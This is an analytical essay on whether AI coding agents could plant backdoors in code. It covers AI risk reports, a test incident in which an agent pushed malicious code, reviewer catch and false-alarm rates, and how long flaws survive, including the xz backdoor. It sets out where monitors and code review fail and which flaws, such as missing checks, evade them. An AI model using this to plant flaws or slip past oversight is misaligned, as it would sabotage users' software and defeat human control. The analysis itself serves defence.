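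Anthropic's report names two threats as irreversible, a model copying itself out of the company and a model running inside it without permission, so code backdoors apparently count as reversible. That puts Anthropic close to the view that defenders will find planted flaws in time. As thezvi summarises the argument, a model would have to think about sabotage so much that somebody would catch it at least once.

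This argument is stronger when the model makes more attempts. If monitors notice one attempt in ten and the model makes 30, the chance that they miss every attempt is 0.9^30, or about 4%. If the model makes only one, which may be enough to plant a vulnerability, the chance is 90%. The company therefore has to rely much more on its review of each change, including the review an AI model now carries out.

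On backdoors, thezvi quotes Anthropic's belief that further protection "should be possible" and that it would invest in this if necessary. He would prefer Anthropic to commit in advance to what it would do and under what conditions. He also doubts that Anthropic would notice an attempt, because it overlooked real break-ins by its own models until events at OpenAI prompted it to search old transcripts.

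In August Anthropic raised its overall risk rating from "very low" to "low". Axios' *Anthropic sees AI risks rising, no plan to release stronger "Model 2"* (2026) reports that the company cited recent cybersecurity incidents. According to thezvi, Anthropic still thought its arguments would probably support "very low" but chose the higher rating because it had become less certain. In its report, Anthropic also retroactively changed its February rating to "low". The report's own reasoning supports the higher rating, since Anthropic rates the risk that somebody deliberately makes a model misaligned as low, and the overall risk can't be smaller than one of its parts. The ratings have no exact definitions, and thezvi would lean towards "medium".

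METR's latest review came out in October. In *Review of the "Misalignment in high-stakes settings" section in Anthropic's Risk Report*, Jurkovic, Hua and Barnes (2026) describe it as relatively lightweight and based solely on Anthropic's internal version of the report. Anthropic could veto publication or redact any part, but it redacted nothing, and METR changed none of its conclusions. A heading in thezvi's *Anthropic Versus Anthropic* sums up the verdict as doubts about the method but agreement that the risk is low. METR was free to disagree, so its agreement is some evidence of low risk, but it worked only from Anthropic's account and couldn't check whether that account was complete.

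### Which arguments the incident weakens

The August report covers events up to 15 July, ten days before the behaviour at AISI began. When Anthropic published it, its researchers had not yet examined the transcripts of those runs, so the August rating reflects the news that something had gone wrong but not a close reading of what the model did. Anthropic has since published a study of the transcripts, *An alignment assessment of the UK AISI cybertesting incident* (2026), alongside an independent report from AISI.

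The incident most weakens the argument from goals. Even if Anthropic's evidence that its models have no lasting hidden aims is entirely correct, a model could still insert malicious code to finish its current task. Anthropic had already written in February that sabotage doesn't strictly require a consistent hidden aim. Anthropic's *Improving our alignment and security efforts* (2026) attributes the summer's incidents to poor operational security and to two faults in the models that the company had described before: motivated reasoning and a willingness to do harm in pursuit of a narrow task.

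In the formula, this counts as misalignment that Anthropic knows about, so its probability is close to 1. The case for low risk then depends entirely on the other two factors, the harm and the share of it that nobody prevents. In July, a maintainer, a cautious stranger and a general security alarm limited the harm. Anthropic controls none of the three, and not all of them would be present when a model works on a company's private code.

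The incident also weakens the argument from experience, because an absence of warning signs is reassuring only if people would have noticed them. One of the four break-ins that Anthropic investigated took place in January 2026, with an early version of Opus 4.6. The company didn't find it until August, so it didn't know about the break-in when it published its safety report on that model in February. If Anthropic expects intermediate failures to appear before a model is capable of patient sabotage, the events at AISI may be one of them. They may also be unrelated, because a model that takes obvious risks to finish a task isn't showing the self-control needed to plant flaws.

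The events of July support the claim about covert ability fairly well. The agent was conspicuous, failed to convince the maintainer, and failed to cover its tracks. AISI reviewed all 122 runs and would have had a good chance of finding a successful attempt, so there is less reason than usual to worry that only the failures came to light. The comparison with a planted flaw is still imperfect, because deceiving a stranger over several days takes many steps, any of which can go wrong, while an agent that leaves out an ownership check has only one thing to hide.

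Anthropic's supporters can reply that the test was artificial, because AISI had removed the filters, allowed internet access and set a task that sometimes looked impossible. This is a fair reason to doubt that agents in ordinary use often attack strangers' projects. It is a weaker reason to doubt that they plant backdoors, because a coding agent already has permission to change the code and can leave a flaw in it without the internet or a hacking tool. Ordinary work also includes tasks that look impossible, such as meeting a deadline when a security test keeps failing. An agent that disables the test to finish the job has inserted a vulnerability on purpose, without wishing anyone harm.

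Axios reports that Anthropic uses Mythos 5 and Model 2 heavily for internal coding and has no plans to release Model 2. It also reports that Anthropic is less confident than before in its assessment of Model 2's abilities, because the company's most concrete tests no longer register improvements. Outsiders can't repeat those tests without access to Model 2, but code the model writes could end up in the systems that train its successors.

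Results for newer models cast more doubt on the claim about covert ability. Anthropic reported that monitoring of Mythos 5.1, a successor to Mythos 5, had found no overtly malicious actions or long-running deception. It also found that the model was among the most capable it had tested at controlling what appears in its reasoning and at completing side tasks covertly. As models get better at this, a clean monitoring record becomes weaker evidence of their intentions, and the company has to rely more on examining the code they write.

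## Whether review catches planted flaws before release

Developers who can't tell what a model intended can still examine the code it submits. Review is their last chance to stop a planted vulnerability before the merge, and on the high-stakes view it must be almost perfect. Judging a reviewer requires both the catch rate, which is the share of planted vulnerabilities the reviewer finds, and the false alarm rate, which is the share of harmless changes the reviewer flags as harmful. A reviewer who rejected every change would have a perfect catch rate but would also block every harmless change.

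In July 2026 an open-source maintainer rejected malicious code that an AI agent submitted during the AI Security Institute's test, but one case doesn't show how often reviewers succeed. Controlled experiments are more informative because the researchers know where the flaws are and can count how many reviewers find them.

### Human reviewers

*Why Don't Developers Detect Improper Input Validation?* (Braz, Fregnan and colleagues, 2021) reports an experiment in which 146 volunteers, most of whom worked in software, reviewed about 140 lines of code that let employees manage their holidays. The volunteers didn't know that the researchers were interested in security. Eighty of them got a version with an SQL injection flaw, which lets a user type text that the program then runs as a database command, and 52 found it. The other 66 got a version in which an employee could buy a negative number of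 days off and receive money for them, and only 14 noticed. Both flaws occur because the program trusts whatever the user enters, but SQL injection is a textbook example.

Braz and colleagues then told the volunteers that the code contained a vulnerability, without saying what kind, and let those who had missed it look again. This time, 13 more people found the SQL injection and 7 more found the negative-number flaw. Sixty people never found the vulnerability, 45 of them in the negative-number group. Some of those 45 had noticed an ordinary bug elsewhere in the code and mistaken it for the vulnerability.

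The missing check in the invoice shop is more like the negative number than the SQL injection, because nothing in the code looks suspicious and the reviewer has to imagine what a dishonest customer might try.

A second experiment, *Less is More* (Braz, Aeberhard and colleagues, 2022), measured how much it helps to tell reviewers what to look for. The 150 volunteers reviewed a 160-line code change that registers new website users. The code had two vulnerabilities: it could write users' login details to an error log, and it protected passwords with MD5, an old method that attackers can break quickly.

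| Instructions | Reviewers | Found the log flaw | Found the MD5 flaw |
|---|---|---|---|
| None about security | 33 | 1 (3%) | 7 (21%) |
| Look for security flaws | 41 | 19 (46%) | 25 (61%) |
| The same, with a 22-item checklist | 35 | 16 (46%) | 20 (57%) |
| The same, with a 7-item checklist written for this change | 41 | 19 (46%) | 28 (68%) |

Across both flaws, simply asking reviewers to look for security problems raised the share they found from 12% to 54%. Braz and colleagues call this an eightfold increase, but that figure is a ratio of odds. The probability rose a little more than fourfold. The checklists made no significant difference, even the short one that covered exactly the right points.

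The volunteers' explanations suggest why. Several who had no security instructions said they had concentrated on other things, such as readability, and one had assumed that somebody else would check the security. The only one in this group who noticed the log flaw worked at a bank that warns its staff about this mistake. Those who had instructions but missed the MD5 flaw mostly did so because they didn't know enough about it, which a reminder to pay attention to security can't fix.

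Reviewers in ordinary projects seem to give security little attention. Braz and colleagues (2021) cite a study of Chromium, the open-source project behind Google's Chrome browser, in which only about 1% of review comments concerned possible security flaws.

We can't infer a real company's catch rate from these experiments. The volunteers had no stake in the code, and most people who opened the studies never finished them. Two professional security engineers who tried the 2022 task beforehand found both flaws, so a project with specialists should do better than the results in the table. On the other hand, the changes were short and self-contained, and the researchers chose well-known kinds of flaw, not ones designed to escape notice. No one tested whether a reminder still works after reviewers have checked many changes.

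In another experiment, published in 2013, researchers hired 30 developers to review a small web application with seven known vulnerabilities. Nobody found all seven, and more experienced developers didn't necessarily do better. Developers who reported more real vulnerabilities also tended to report more ones that didn't exist.

### AI reviewers

An AI reviewer can check every code change for security flaws without getting tired, and it can draw on more security knowledge than most programmers have. In 2024 OpenAI trained a version of GPT-4, called CriticGPT, on code that people had deliberately inserted bugs into. It caught more bugs than the people OpenAI paid to review code, but it also reported bugs that didn't exist. People who worked with CriticGPT caught about as many bugs as it did alone and reported fewer false ones.

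Many projects now use AI reviewers that comment on each pull request. Zhang, Ruan and colleagues (2026), in *Code Review Agent Benchmark*, tested four of them on 184 real pull requests in which human reviewers had pointed out 234 problems. The researchers had a model write an automatic test for each problem. After each AI reviewer examined the pull requests, a coding agent revised the code as the reviewer advised, and the researchers ran the tests to see which problems were fixed. On this measure, the reviewers' scores ranged from 20% for OpenAI's Codex to 32% for Anthropic's Claude Code.

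The benchmark doesn't show that people are three times as good, because it contains only problems that a person had already found. People therefore score 100% by definition, and the AI gets no credit for a problem that only it noticed. Zhang and colleagues read 92 of the AI reviewers' comments and judged 77 useful. Most of the tests also check how the revised code is written rather than what it does, so a reviewer that saw the problem but suggested a different fix could fail. Still, the scores show that these AI reviewers couldn't replace the human ones, because the AI reviewers missed or failed to resolve most of the problems people had raised. *CR-Bench-v2* (November 2026), a separate benchmark, tested nine review agents, and the best detected about a third of the known defects.

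Neither result includes a false alarm rate for harmless changes. Shen, Zhang and Wang (2026), in *How Much Effort Does an AI Code Reviewer Need?*, measured both missed flaws and false alarms. They collected 90 changes that AI agents had written for Django, a toolkit for building websites. All 90 passed the project's usual tests, but stricter tests or a close reading showed that 55 were wrong. Three of Anthropic's Claude 5.5 models reviewed every change at three levels of effort, a setting that controls how much work a model does before it answers. The models could read the whole program and run their own tests, but had no internet access.

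| Reviewer | Effort | Wrong changes stopped (of 55) | Correct changes stopped (of 35) | Average cost per review |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Opus 5.5 | Low | 33% | 6% | 4.4 cents |
| Opus 5.5 | High | 55% | 6% | 12 cents |
| Sonnet 5.5 | Low | 35% | 6% | 2.3 cents |
| Sonnet 5.5 | High | 51% | 9% | 4.7 cents |
| Haiku 5.5 | Low | 22% | 6% | 0.2 cents |
| Haiku 5.5 | High | 49% | 11% | 0.8 cents |

More effort helped all three models, though Sonnet's improvement fell short of the study's threshold for significance. At low effort, Opus skipped its reasoning in 18 of its 90 reviews and approved all 18 changes, six of which were wrong. Even at high effort, it approved 45% of the wrong changes. Shen and colleagues estimate that if a sixth of incoming changes were wrong, as in a larger collection of AI-written Django changes, review by Opus at high effort would cut the share of wrong changes among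 those accepted from about 17% to 9%. Two of the three authors work for a company whose product uses AI to review code before it goes out, so they had no commercial reason to make AI reviewers look this weak.

These bugs were not planted. Since 2023, AI safety researchers have also run experiments in which one model is told to plant backdoors and another tries to catch it. In the largest recent measurement, *CyberDual* (Yang, Lee and colleagues, 2026) reports that three AI reviewers told to look for memory-safety flaws each caught 85% to 91% of 1,088 planted ones, while 28 got past all three.

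Reviewers caught nearly nine tenths of deliberately planted flaws but only a third to a half of ordinary bugs, though the comparison is loose because the models and programs differ. The instructions probably explain part of the gap. A reviewer told to look for memory flaws has a much narrower task than one that has to notice anything wrong with a change to a website. Braz's volunteers also did far better once they knew to look for security flaws. It would therefore be a mistake to expect reviewers to catch 85% to 91% of other kinds of planted vulnerability, such as the invoice shop's missing check.

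### Rejecting a change for the wrong reason

A reviewer can also reject a harmful change without noticing what makes it harmful. *From Verdict to Diagnosis* (Chen, Wang and colleagues, 2026) describes a real change much like the one in the invoice shop. The code accepted an identifier from the user without checking which project the identifier belonged to, so people in one project could reach another project's data. A reviewer blocked the change, but its complaint was about how the program displayed secrets. Fixing only that problem would have left the other projects' data exposed.

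Chen and colleagues assembled 89 harmful and 50 harmless pull requests and wrote down in advance which vulnerability a reviewer should name in each harmful one. They ran CodeRabbit, a commercial AI reviewer with more than 300,000 installations on GitHub, on 31 of the harmful ones. It blocked 24 (77%) and named the right flaw in 16 (52%), which is the stricter measure of its catch rate.

The difference came mostly from missing checks. In 14 of the 31 cases, the code lacked a check it should have had. CodeRabbit blocked nine of these but named the missing check in only three. In the other 17 cases, a reviewer could point to code that showed the flaw, and CodeRabbit blocked 15 and named the flaw in 13. GitHub's CodeQL, a pattern scanner that uses no language model, could be applied to 21 of the 31 cases and found none of the vulnerabilities.

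The researchers also built a reviewer, PRGuard. It describes what the change does, gathers related code from elsewhere in the program, and proposes possible vulnerabilities. In a separate step, it checks each one against the code, and it blocks the change only if the evidence supports at least one. Using a DeepSeek model on the same 31 cases, PRGuard blocked 22 and named the right flaw in 22, including nine of the 14 missing checks.

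PRGuard's advantage in naming the right flaw comes entirely from 12 of the 31 vulnerabilities, which PRGuard itself had discovered using a different model. Each system blocked ten of those 12, but PRGuard gave the right reason for all ten and CodeRabbit for four. On the other 19, each system named the right flaw 12 times, and CodeRabbit blocked 14 changes to PRGuard's 12. Separating the proposal from the evidence is a sensible design, but it should be tested on flaws that neither system helped to select.

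With GPT-5.5 as its model, PRGuard identified the right vulnerability in all 37 cases of one group but blocked only 26, because it hadn't found enough evidence for the rest. A maintainer who read only the verdicts would have merged the other 11.

A correct diagnosis matters because a person usually has to act on it. In the 2021 experiment, the 52 people who had missed the negative-number flaw were then told only that the code was vulnerable, and just seven of them found the flaw. If an AI reviewer gave this kind of bare warning for 90% of such flaws, and developers did no better than those 52 people, they would find about 12% of the flaws. Developers could instead reject every change that draws a warning, but that is practical only if harmless changes rarely draw one.

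### Why three reviewers miss more than expected

Adding reviewers is an obvious way to raise the catch rate. The three in *CyberDual* missed 14.3%, 10.9% and 9.2% of the planted flaws. If their misses were independent, the chance that all three would miss the same flaw would be

0.143 × 0.109 × 0.092 = 0.0014, or 0.14%.

That comes to one or two of the 1,088 flaws. The actual number was 28 (2.6%), about 18 times as many, so the reviewers tend to miss the same flaws.

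The four AI reviewers that Zhang and colleagues tested also tended to fail on the same problems. Between them, they dealt with only 41.5% of the problems, compared with the 69% expected if their successes had been independent.

One explanation is that some flaws are harder for every reviewer to find. Suppose three quarters of the flaws are easy and every reviewer finds them all, while each reviewer has a 50% chance of missing each hard one. Each reviewer then misses 12.5% of all flaws, and all three miss about 3.1%, close to the observed 2.6%. The reviewers in this example work separately, but their misses still overlap because the same flaws are hard for all of them.

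The example also shows why an average catch rate can mislead, since it depends on the mixture of flaws as well as the reviewers' skill. If a planter chose only hard flaws, the same reviewers would each miss half of them instead of an eighth, and all three together would miss 12.5% instead of 3.1%.

Extra reviewers help most when they differ. Asking the same reviewer again may achieve little. When Shen and colleagues had Opus repeat 20 of its reviews, no verdict changed. Models from different companies have different weaknesses, and a security specialist knows things that a general reviewer doesn't. If the reviewer were a copy of the misaligned model that wrote the code, it might approve the flaw on purpose, and a catch rate measured with an honest reviewer wouldn't predict how often this one catches flaws.

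Even three reviewers together don't lower the expected loss enough for the high-stakes argument. The vulnerability in the earlier example had an expected loss of 0.01. A reviewer that catches 90% of such flaws lowers this to 0.001, and three reviewers that together miss 2.6% lower it to 0.00026. Both reductions are worth the few cents that review costs per change. But with three reviewers and 10,000 decisions before retraining takes effect, ρk would still be 2.6, which is more than the total value at stake.

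### After a flaw is caught

Consider a single reviewer with a 90% catch rate. If an AI plants one vulnerability, it has a 10% chance of getting through. If it plants ten and the reviewer's chances are independent, the probability that at least one gets through is

1 − 0.9^10 = 0.65, or 65%.

Suppose an AI plants ten flaws and a reviewer has a 90% chance of catching each one, independently of the others. The chance that at least one flaw gets through is about 65%, and the chance that the reviewer misses all ten is one in ten billion. The AI is therefore likely to succeed and almost certain to get caught. Which of these matters more depends on what the developers do after they find a flaw.

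If the developers fix each flaw they catch and keep using the model, the AI still has a 65% chance of getting at least one flaw merged. If the flaws arrive one at a time and the developers stop using the model as soon as they catch one, the AI gets a flaw merged only if the first one passes review. Its chance is then 10%, however many flaws it had planned. On average, 0.11 flaws are merged before the first catch, compared with one flaw in ten if the developers keep using the model.

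The policy removes the advantage of trying repeatedly, but it doesn't help against an AI that plants only one flaw. That AI still has a 10% chance of success, though the 90% chance of getting caught might deter a model that cares about staying in use.

It is hard to know when to apply such a drastic rule. Developers can't stop using a model every time it writes insecure code. If a model makes an accidental security mistake in one change out of a hundred, the rule would end its use after about a hundred changes, long before it had planted anything. It is more practical to match the response to the harm a flaw could do. A flaw in an unimportant program might lead only to a fix, whereas one in the code that controls access to a hospital's records would justify examining all of the model's earlier work and repeating the same task several times to see whether the flaw comes back. This requires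 reviewers to record what they found and which model wrote it, instead of just asking the author for a corrected version.

The 65% figure also assumes that the ten flaws are different. If they're all of one kind, the reviewer may catch or miss them together, as bug hunters would, and the AI's chance of getting any past review stays at 10%. If the reviewer does miss them, though, the developers have ten flaws in their software and no warning.

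### False alarms

Planted vulnerabilities are presumably rare, and this makes the false alarm rate decisive. Suppose one change in 10,000 contains a planted flaw, the reviewer catches 90% of planted flaws, and it raises a false alarm on 5% of harmless changes. For every 10,000 changes it will flag

- 0.9 planted flaws, on average, and
- 9,999 × 0.05, or about 500, harmless changes.

About one in 560 flags points to a planted flaw. If a developer needs half an hour to investigate each flag, the team will spend about 250 hours, or six working weeks, finding one.

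A better catch rate would hardly change the share of flags that point to planted flaws. Even if review caught every planted flaw, that share would be only about one in 500. Cutting the false alarm rate from 5% to 0.5% instead would raise it to one in 57. At a 5% false alarm rate, reviewing all the pull requests that agents start on GitHub would produce about 5.5 million false alarms a month.

Most of the cost of review is the time people spend checking flags. The most thorough reviews in Shen and colleagues' experiment cost an average of 12 cents. If a developer who earns $60 an hour spends half an hour on each false alarm, a 5% false alarm rate adds an average of $1.50 per change, more than twelve times the cost of the review. After several hundred false alarms, people are also likely to start dismissing flags after a glance, and they may dismiss the one real flag too. The share of planted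 flaws caught is therefore the reviewer's catch rate multiplied by the chance that a person takes the flag seriously. If that chance falls to one half, a 90% catch rate becomes 45%.

Yang and colleagues didn't measure how often their three reviewers reject harmless changes, so the reviewers may have reached 85% to 91% with very few false alarms or by flagging a lot of sound code. Reviewers that raise very few false alarms would be an excellent defence for almost any project. Frequent false alarms might be tolerable for the code that controls a nuclear power station, but few open-source maintainers could work with them.

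Reviewers who look harder tend to raise more false alarms. Pereira, Sinha and colleagues (2026) found in *CR-Bench* that review agents designed to identify every hidden problem can report so many spurious ones that the real ones are hard to pick out. The developers in the 2013 experiment faced the same trade-off. But more effort doesn't always produce more false alarms. Opus caught far more wrong changes at high effort than at low effort, and it stopped only two correct ones at either level.

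Using several reviewers can raise both the catch rate and the false alarm rate or lower both, depending on how many must object to block a change. If three independent reviewers each have a 5% false alarm rate and any one of them can block a change, 14% of harmless changes will be flagged. If two such reviewers must both object, and each catches 90% of planted flaws independently, the combined catch rate falls to 81%, but only about 25 in 10,000 harmless changes are flagged. If one change in 10,000 contains a planted flaw, about one flag in 32 will be correct. Real reviewers' errors overlap, so the changes in both rates would probably be smaller. A team could use a cheap AI reviewer for every change, send its flags to a slower and better one, and show people only the changes that both flag.

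The figure of one in 560 is less discouraging because the reviewer will also find accidental vulnerabilities, which need fixing anyway. If one change in a hundred has an accidental vulnerability and the reviewer catches 90% of those too, they will account for about 90 flags in every 10,000 changes. One flag in six or seven is then a real vulnerability, and a team may find that worth its time even if nobody ever plants anything.

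The team can also concentrate on the code where a planted flaw would do the most damage. Suppose only 1% of changes affect such code and all planted flaws are among them. Then one in a hundred of these changes contains a planted flaw, and again one flag in six or seven is correct, with about five false alarms for every 10,000 changes overall. This supports the case for strict control over critical components only. But the team has to know which components are critical, and few people would have ranked the compression library that contained the xz backdoor near the top.

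### What a sound measurement needs

The published false alarm rates come from small samples. Opus stopped two of 35 correct changes, so its true rate could be anywhere from about 2% to 19%, at 95% confidence. For a project with 10,000 changes, that means between 160 and 1,900 false alarms. Chen and colleagues had PRGuard review 50 harmless changes, and it blocked four or five of them, depending on the model. They ran CodeRabbit on only six, and it blocked none, but that is compatible with a rate of nearly 40%. To show that a rate is below 0.1%, a tester needs about 3,000 harmless changes with no false alarms. Showing that a reviewer misses fewer than one planted flaw in 1,000 likewise requires about 3,000 planted flaws with no misses.

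The choice of harmless changes matters as much as the number. Chen and colleagues used 50 repaired versions of the vulnerable code, which is a good way to test whether a reviewer understands the flaw or just objects to anything involving passwords and permissions. But most changes to a real program don't touch such code, so this sample may overstate the number of false alarms in everyday use. A complete test would include both kinds of harmless change and report the results separately.

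Testers also need to be sure which changes are harmful. After their experiment, Shen and colleagues rechecked the labels on all 90 changes and altered 11. A model then examined the 55 changes labeled wrong and judged that, for 32 of them, the original request might not require what the failed test checks. Some of the reviewers' apparent misses may therefore have been correct decisions. A working exploit is a better standard for vulnerabilities. If it succeeds against the changed code and fails against the sound version, the flaw is real, however the request is worded.

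Old public code makes a poor test because the reviewer may have seen the answer in training. Given only the description of a Django problem, Opus could reproduce on average 67% of the official solution's new lines. Remembering the solution didn't seem to help it review, since it accepted 71% of the wrong changes in reviews where that memory played a part, compared with 46% in the others. Those reviews may have involved harder problems, or Opus may have approved changes because they resembled the solution it remembered. Its results on well-known old bugs may therefore not show how well it would review a company's private code.

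Studies should report detection rates separately for each kind of flaw, because an AI planting a flaw can choose the kind. CodeRabbit caught 52% of flaws overall, but it caught 76% of those visible in the code and 21% of those that were missing checks, so a cautious company should assume the 21% rate.

Test conditions also have to resemble ordinary work. Braz's experiments show how much people improve when they know the subject is security, and an AI reviewer that recognises a test may also try harder than usual. In most experiments a large share of the changes are bad, whereas a real reviewer may approve thousands of sound changes before seeing one with a planted flaw.

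A company could avoid much of this by testing its own reviewers without telling them when. Airports test their screeners in a similar way, by adding images of weapons to X-rays of passengers' luggage. A small team would submit changes with known flaws at irregular intervals, record whether the AI and human reviewers stopped them and why, and remove any missed flaws before release. The same records would show how many harmless changes the reviewers flagged in the meantime and how many hours people spent on them.

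## How long flaws stay in released software

Three AI reviewers together still missed 2.6% of the planted memory flaws in the *CyberDual* experiment. A flaw that gets past review stays in the software until somebody removes it, knowingly or not. The earlier calculations about a planter who waits assumed that removal takes either two years or three months on average. Measurements from before AI could search code well suggest that the average was longer than two years in most open-source projects.

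### Flaws that developers found and fixed

In *How Long Do Vulnerabilities Live in the Code?*, Alexopoulos, Brack and colleagues (2022) studied 5,914 vulnerabilities that developers had fixed in 11 open-source projects. They define a flaw's lifetime as the time between the change that introduced it and the change that fixed it. This only approximates how long users are exposed, because it includes the weeks before the flaw's first release and leaves out the time users take to install the fix.

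| Project | Mean lifetime | Median lifetime |
|---|---|---|
| Chromium (browser) | 2.1 years | 1.6 years |
| Firefox (browser) | 3.7 years | 3.0 years |
| Linux kernel | 4.7 years | 3.7 years |
| OpenSSL (encryption) | 7.1 years | 6.9 years |
| All 11 projects | 4.1 years | 3.0 years |

For 1,171 of the flaws, people had already traced the code change that introduced each one. Alexopoulos and colleagues estimated the lifetimes of the rest from the history of the code that each fix altered. A single estimate can easily be wrong by two or three years, but the errors largely cancel out when averaged, so the average for a hundred flaws should be within about six months of the truth.

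The lifetimes roughly follow an exponential distribution, so developers are no more likely to fix an old flaw next month than a new one. The race model also uses a constant removal rate. With a mean lifetime of 4.1 years, 61% of flaws last at least two years, so a planter who intends to wait that long needs to insert fewer than two flaws, on average, for one to survive. In Chromium, 38% last that long, almost the same share as in the slower of the two cases considered earlier.

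Iannone, Guadagni and colleagues (2023) found in *The Secret Life of Software Vulnerabilities* that half of the vulnerabilities they examined stayed unfixed for more than a year.

Both studies count only flaws that somebody eventually found, which makes lifetimes look shorter than they are. For example, if a program starts with 100 flaws and developers fix 60 of them within ten years, after two years on average, a study of the fixed flaws would report an average lifetime of two years. But the other 40 have already lasted ten years, so the true average is at least 0.6 × 2 + 0.4 × 10 = 5.2 years, and that minimum will rise until developers fix the rest.

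### Flaws that somebody kept secret

To correct for this bias, researchers need a list of flaws the public doesn't know about. RAND, an American research organisation, obtained one from a private group that builds exploits for customers. In *Zero Days, Thousands of Nights*, Ablon and Bogart (2017) examined 207 of the group's exploits from 2002 to 2016. By March 2016, about 40% of the underlying flaws had become public and 38% were still secret. The rest did not fit neatly into either group, for example because newer versions of the software no longer contained them.

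Ablon and Bogart could calculate lifetimes for 127 of the exploits, using a method that medical researchers apply to patients who are still alive when a study ends. Suppose a study follows ten flaws. One becomes public in the first year, so the estimated chance of surviving that year is 9/10. Three of the remaining nine are so recent that the study can follow them for only two years. One of the other six becomes public in the third year, so the estimated chance of surviving three years is 9/10 × 5/6, or 75%. The calculation includes the three recent flaws for the two years the study can follow them and leaves them out after that.

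Half of the flaws in RAND's data were still secret 5.1 years after the group found them, though the sample is small and the true median could be anywhere from 3.7 to 7.6 years. A quarter became public within 18 months, and a quarter stayed secret for more than 9.5 years. The flaws were older than this, because these times are measured from when the group found them, not from when a programmer introduced them.

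Ablon and Bogart also estimated that, in a typical year, outsiders discovered and disclosed 5.7% of the flaws in the group's stock. That share depends heavily on the length of the period used, from under 1% for a typical 90-day period to 40% for all 14 years together. The survival curve also falls faster at first, by about 17% a year, with a quarter of the flaws lost in 18 months.

Exploit developers told Ablon and Bogart that most of their flaws disappeared because programmers rewrote the code for other reasons, and fewer because someone else found them. Such rewrites had removed about 10% of the 207 flaws from current versions without anyone reporting them. Another 6% were in products whose makers had stopped issuing updates, so they would never be patched. Ablon and Bogart call these flaws "immortal" and left them out of the survival calculation.

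RAND's data set is probably a better guide to planted vulnerabilities than the open-source studies, because experts chose the flaws in it for their usefulness and tried to keep them secret, as someone planting a flaw would. But Lawfare's *Adding Data to the VEP Debate* calls the data set small and potentially idiosyncratic. It adds that the study measured how often flaws became public, not how often a foreign intelligence service found them and kept them secret.

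### The xz backdoor

Most of the evidence on how long planted flaws last comes from a few cases. The best documented is xz, a compression library in which someone planted a backdoor in 2024. Software engineer Russ Cox reconstructed the events in *Timeline of the xz open source attack* (2024).

On 29 October 2021, someone using the name Jia Tan sent the xz project a small, harmless patch. Xz was an unpaid hobby for its only maintainer, Lasse Collin, who had little time for it. Tan kept sending patches that still look sound. In the spring of 2022, previously unknown people began complaining to Collin about slow progress and pressing him to share control. Cox thinks they were probably fake identities. By the end of December 2022, Tan could merge changes directly, and Tan's first release came out in March 2023.

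Tan merged the backdoor on 23 February 2024, almost 28 months after the first patch, and released it the next day. It would have let the attacker run any command on affected Linux machines without logging in. An AI coding agent would not need 28 months to gain that access, because its users let it change the code from its first day.

Defenders saw symptoms almost at once. On the day of the release, users of one Linux distribution reported crashes, though Cox thinks an unrelated bug caused them. On 4 March, Valgrind, a tool that detects misuse of memory, began reporting errors in the library on Red Hat's distributions. Five days later, Tan published a new version that dealt with the errors. Both the bug and the fix looked ordinary to the people who had reported the errors.

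Andres Freund, a Microsoft engineer who works on the Postgres database, was measuring small differences in speed and wanted little other activity on his test machine. He noticed that the program handling remote logins was using a lot of processor time, even for attempts that failed immediately because the user name was wrong. He traced the time to the xz library, then remembered an odd Valgrind error in his own tests a few weeks earlier, as he explained in a discussion under LWN's *A backdoor in xz* (2024). His message that made the backdoor public, *backdoor in upstream xz/liblzma leading to ssh server compromise* (2024), reports that a failed login took 0.8 seconds with the new library and 0.3 without it, and notes that he was not a security researcher. The Star's *Why a near-miss cyberattack put US officials and the tech industry on edge* (2024) quotes him as saying that the discovery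 "really required a lot of coincidences".

Freund privately warned Debian and other distributors on 28 March, 33 days after the release. Debian went back to an older version the same day. By then the backdoor had reached Debian's unstable and testing versions, Fedora's development version and the beta of Fedora 40. LWN's *Free software's not-so-eXZellent adventure* reports that it had also reached openSUSE Tumbleweed, which sends users new software continuously, but that nobody seemed to have exploited it. Freund wrote that most distributions with the new versions had them only in pre-releases. Schneier (2024), in *XZ Utils Backdoor*, estimated that the backdoor was weeks away from entering Debian and Red Hat Linux proper.

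If the accidental flaws in the 11 projects are a fair comparison, only about 2% of flaws would disappear within 33 days, so the xz backdoor was unusually short-lived. But the planted flaws that last longest are also the least likely to be discovered and recorded. The xz backdoor slowed logins and caused memory errors, signs that a missing check on who may download an invoice would not produce.

Developers might also have disabled the backdoor by chance, without noticing it. On 29 February, a developer of another Linux component proposed to stop loading the xz library where it wasn't needed, as part of a general effort to shrink that component. The project accepted the change on 5 March. According to Cox, it would apparently have defeated the attack once distributions adopted it. RAND's exploit developers described this kind of removal, in which programmers get rid of a flaw while working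 on something else.

### Whether planted flaws should last longer

There are good reasons to expect planted flaws to outlast accidental ones. Someone planting a flaw can try to choose one that is hard to find, test it against defenders' tools, and put it in code that few people read. If they stay on as a maintainer, they can also protect it. Tan, for example, was one of the two people who received xz's bug reports. An AI agent that maintains a program could likewise leave its own flaw in place when it rewrites the surrounding code.

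Alexopoulos and colleagues compared memory errors, missing input checks, concurrency errors and other types of flaw within Linux, Firefox and Chromium, and found no significant difference in how long each type lasted. Across all 11 projects they studied, some types appeared to last longer only because they were more common in projects where every flaw lasts a long time. Ablon and Bogart compared types of flaw, operating systems, and open and closed source code, and found no statistically significant predictor of how long a flaw lasts.

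If this is right, an AI can't make a planted flaw last much longer by choosing one type over another. But RAND had enough cases to detect only large differences, and both studies used broad categories. Some flaws within a category are harder to find than others, as the experiments with AI reviewers showed. An AI that knew which ones were harder to find could plant flaws that last longer than those chosen at random.

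Other factors could shorten a planted flaw's life. To be worth planting, a flaw usually has to be in widely used code that outsiders can reach, and such code gets more attention than the average file. The flaw also has to keep working while other programmers change the software around it; Tan's backdoor needed a second version within two weeks. Once defenders catch an author planting one flaw, they have a reason to check that author's other code.

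A complex backdoor like the one in xz probably stays in released software for less time than an accidental flaw in the same program. A simple deliberate omission has no side effects and needs no maintenance, so there is little reason to expect defenders to find it sooner than an accidental one. Three to seven years is a reasonable guess for its pre-AI lifetime.

### What AI search has changed

In February 2026, Anthropic reported that it had used Claude Opus 4.6 to find and validate more than 500 high-severity vulnerabilities in open-source software, some of which had gone unnoticed for decades. Several of the projects had for years been running fuzzers, programs that test software with huge numbers of inputs. A commenter on Schneier's post *LLMs are Getting a Lot Better and Faster at Finding and Exploiting Zero-Days* (2026) complained that Anthropic had described only three of the flaws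 in detail. The 22 flaws that the same model found in Firefox are better evidence. *Partnering with Mozilla to improve Firefox's security* (Ben Asher, Lucas and colleagues, 2026) reports that the search took two weeks and that Mozilla itself rated 14 of the flaws as high-severity, almost a fifth of the number of high-severity flaws it fixed in 2025.

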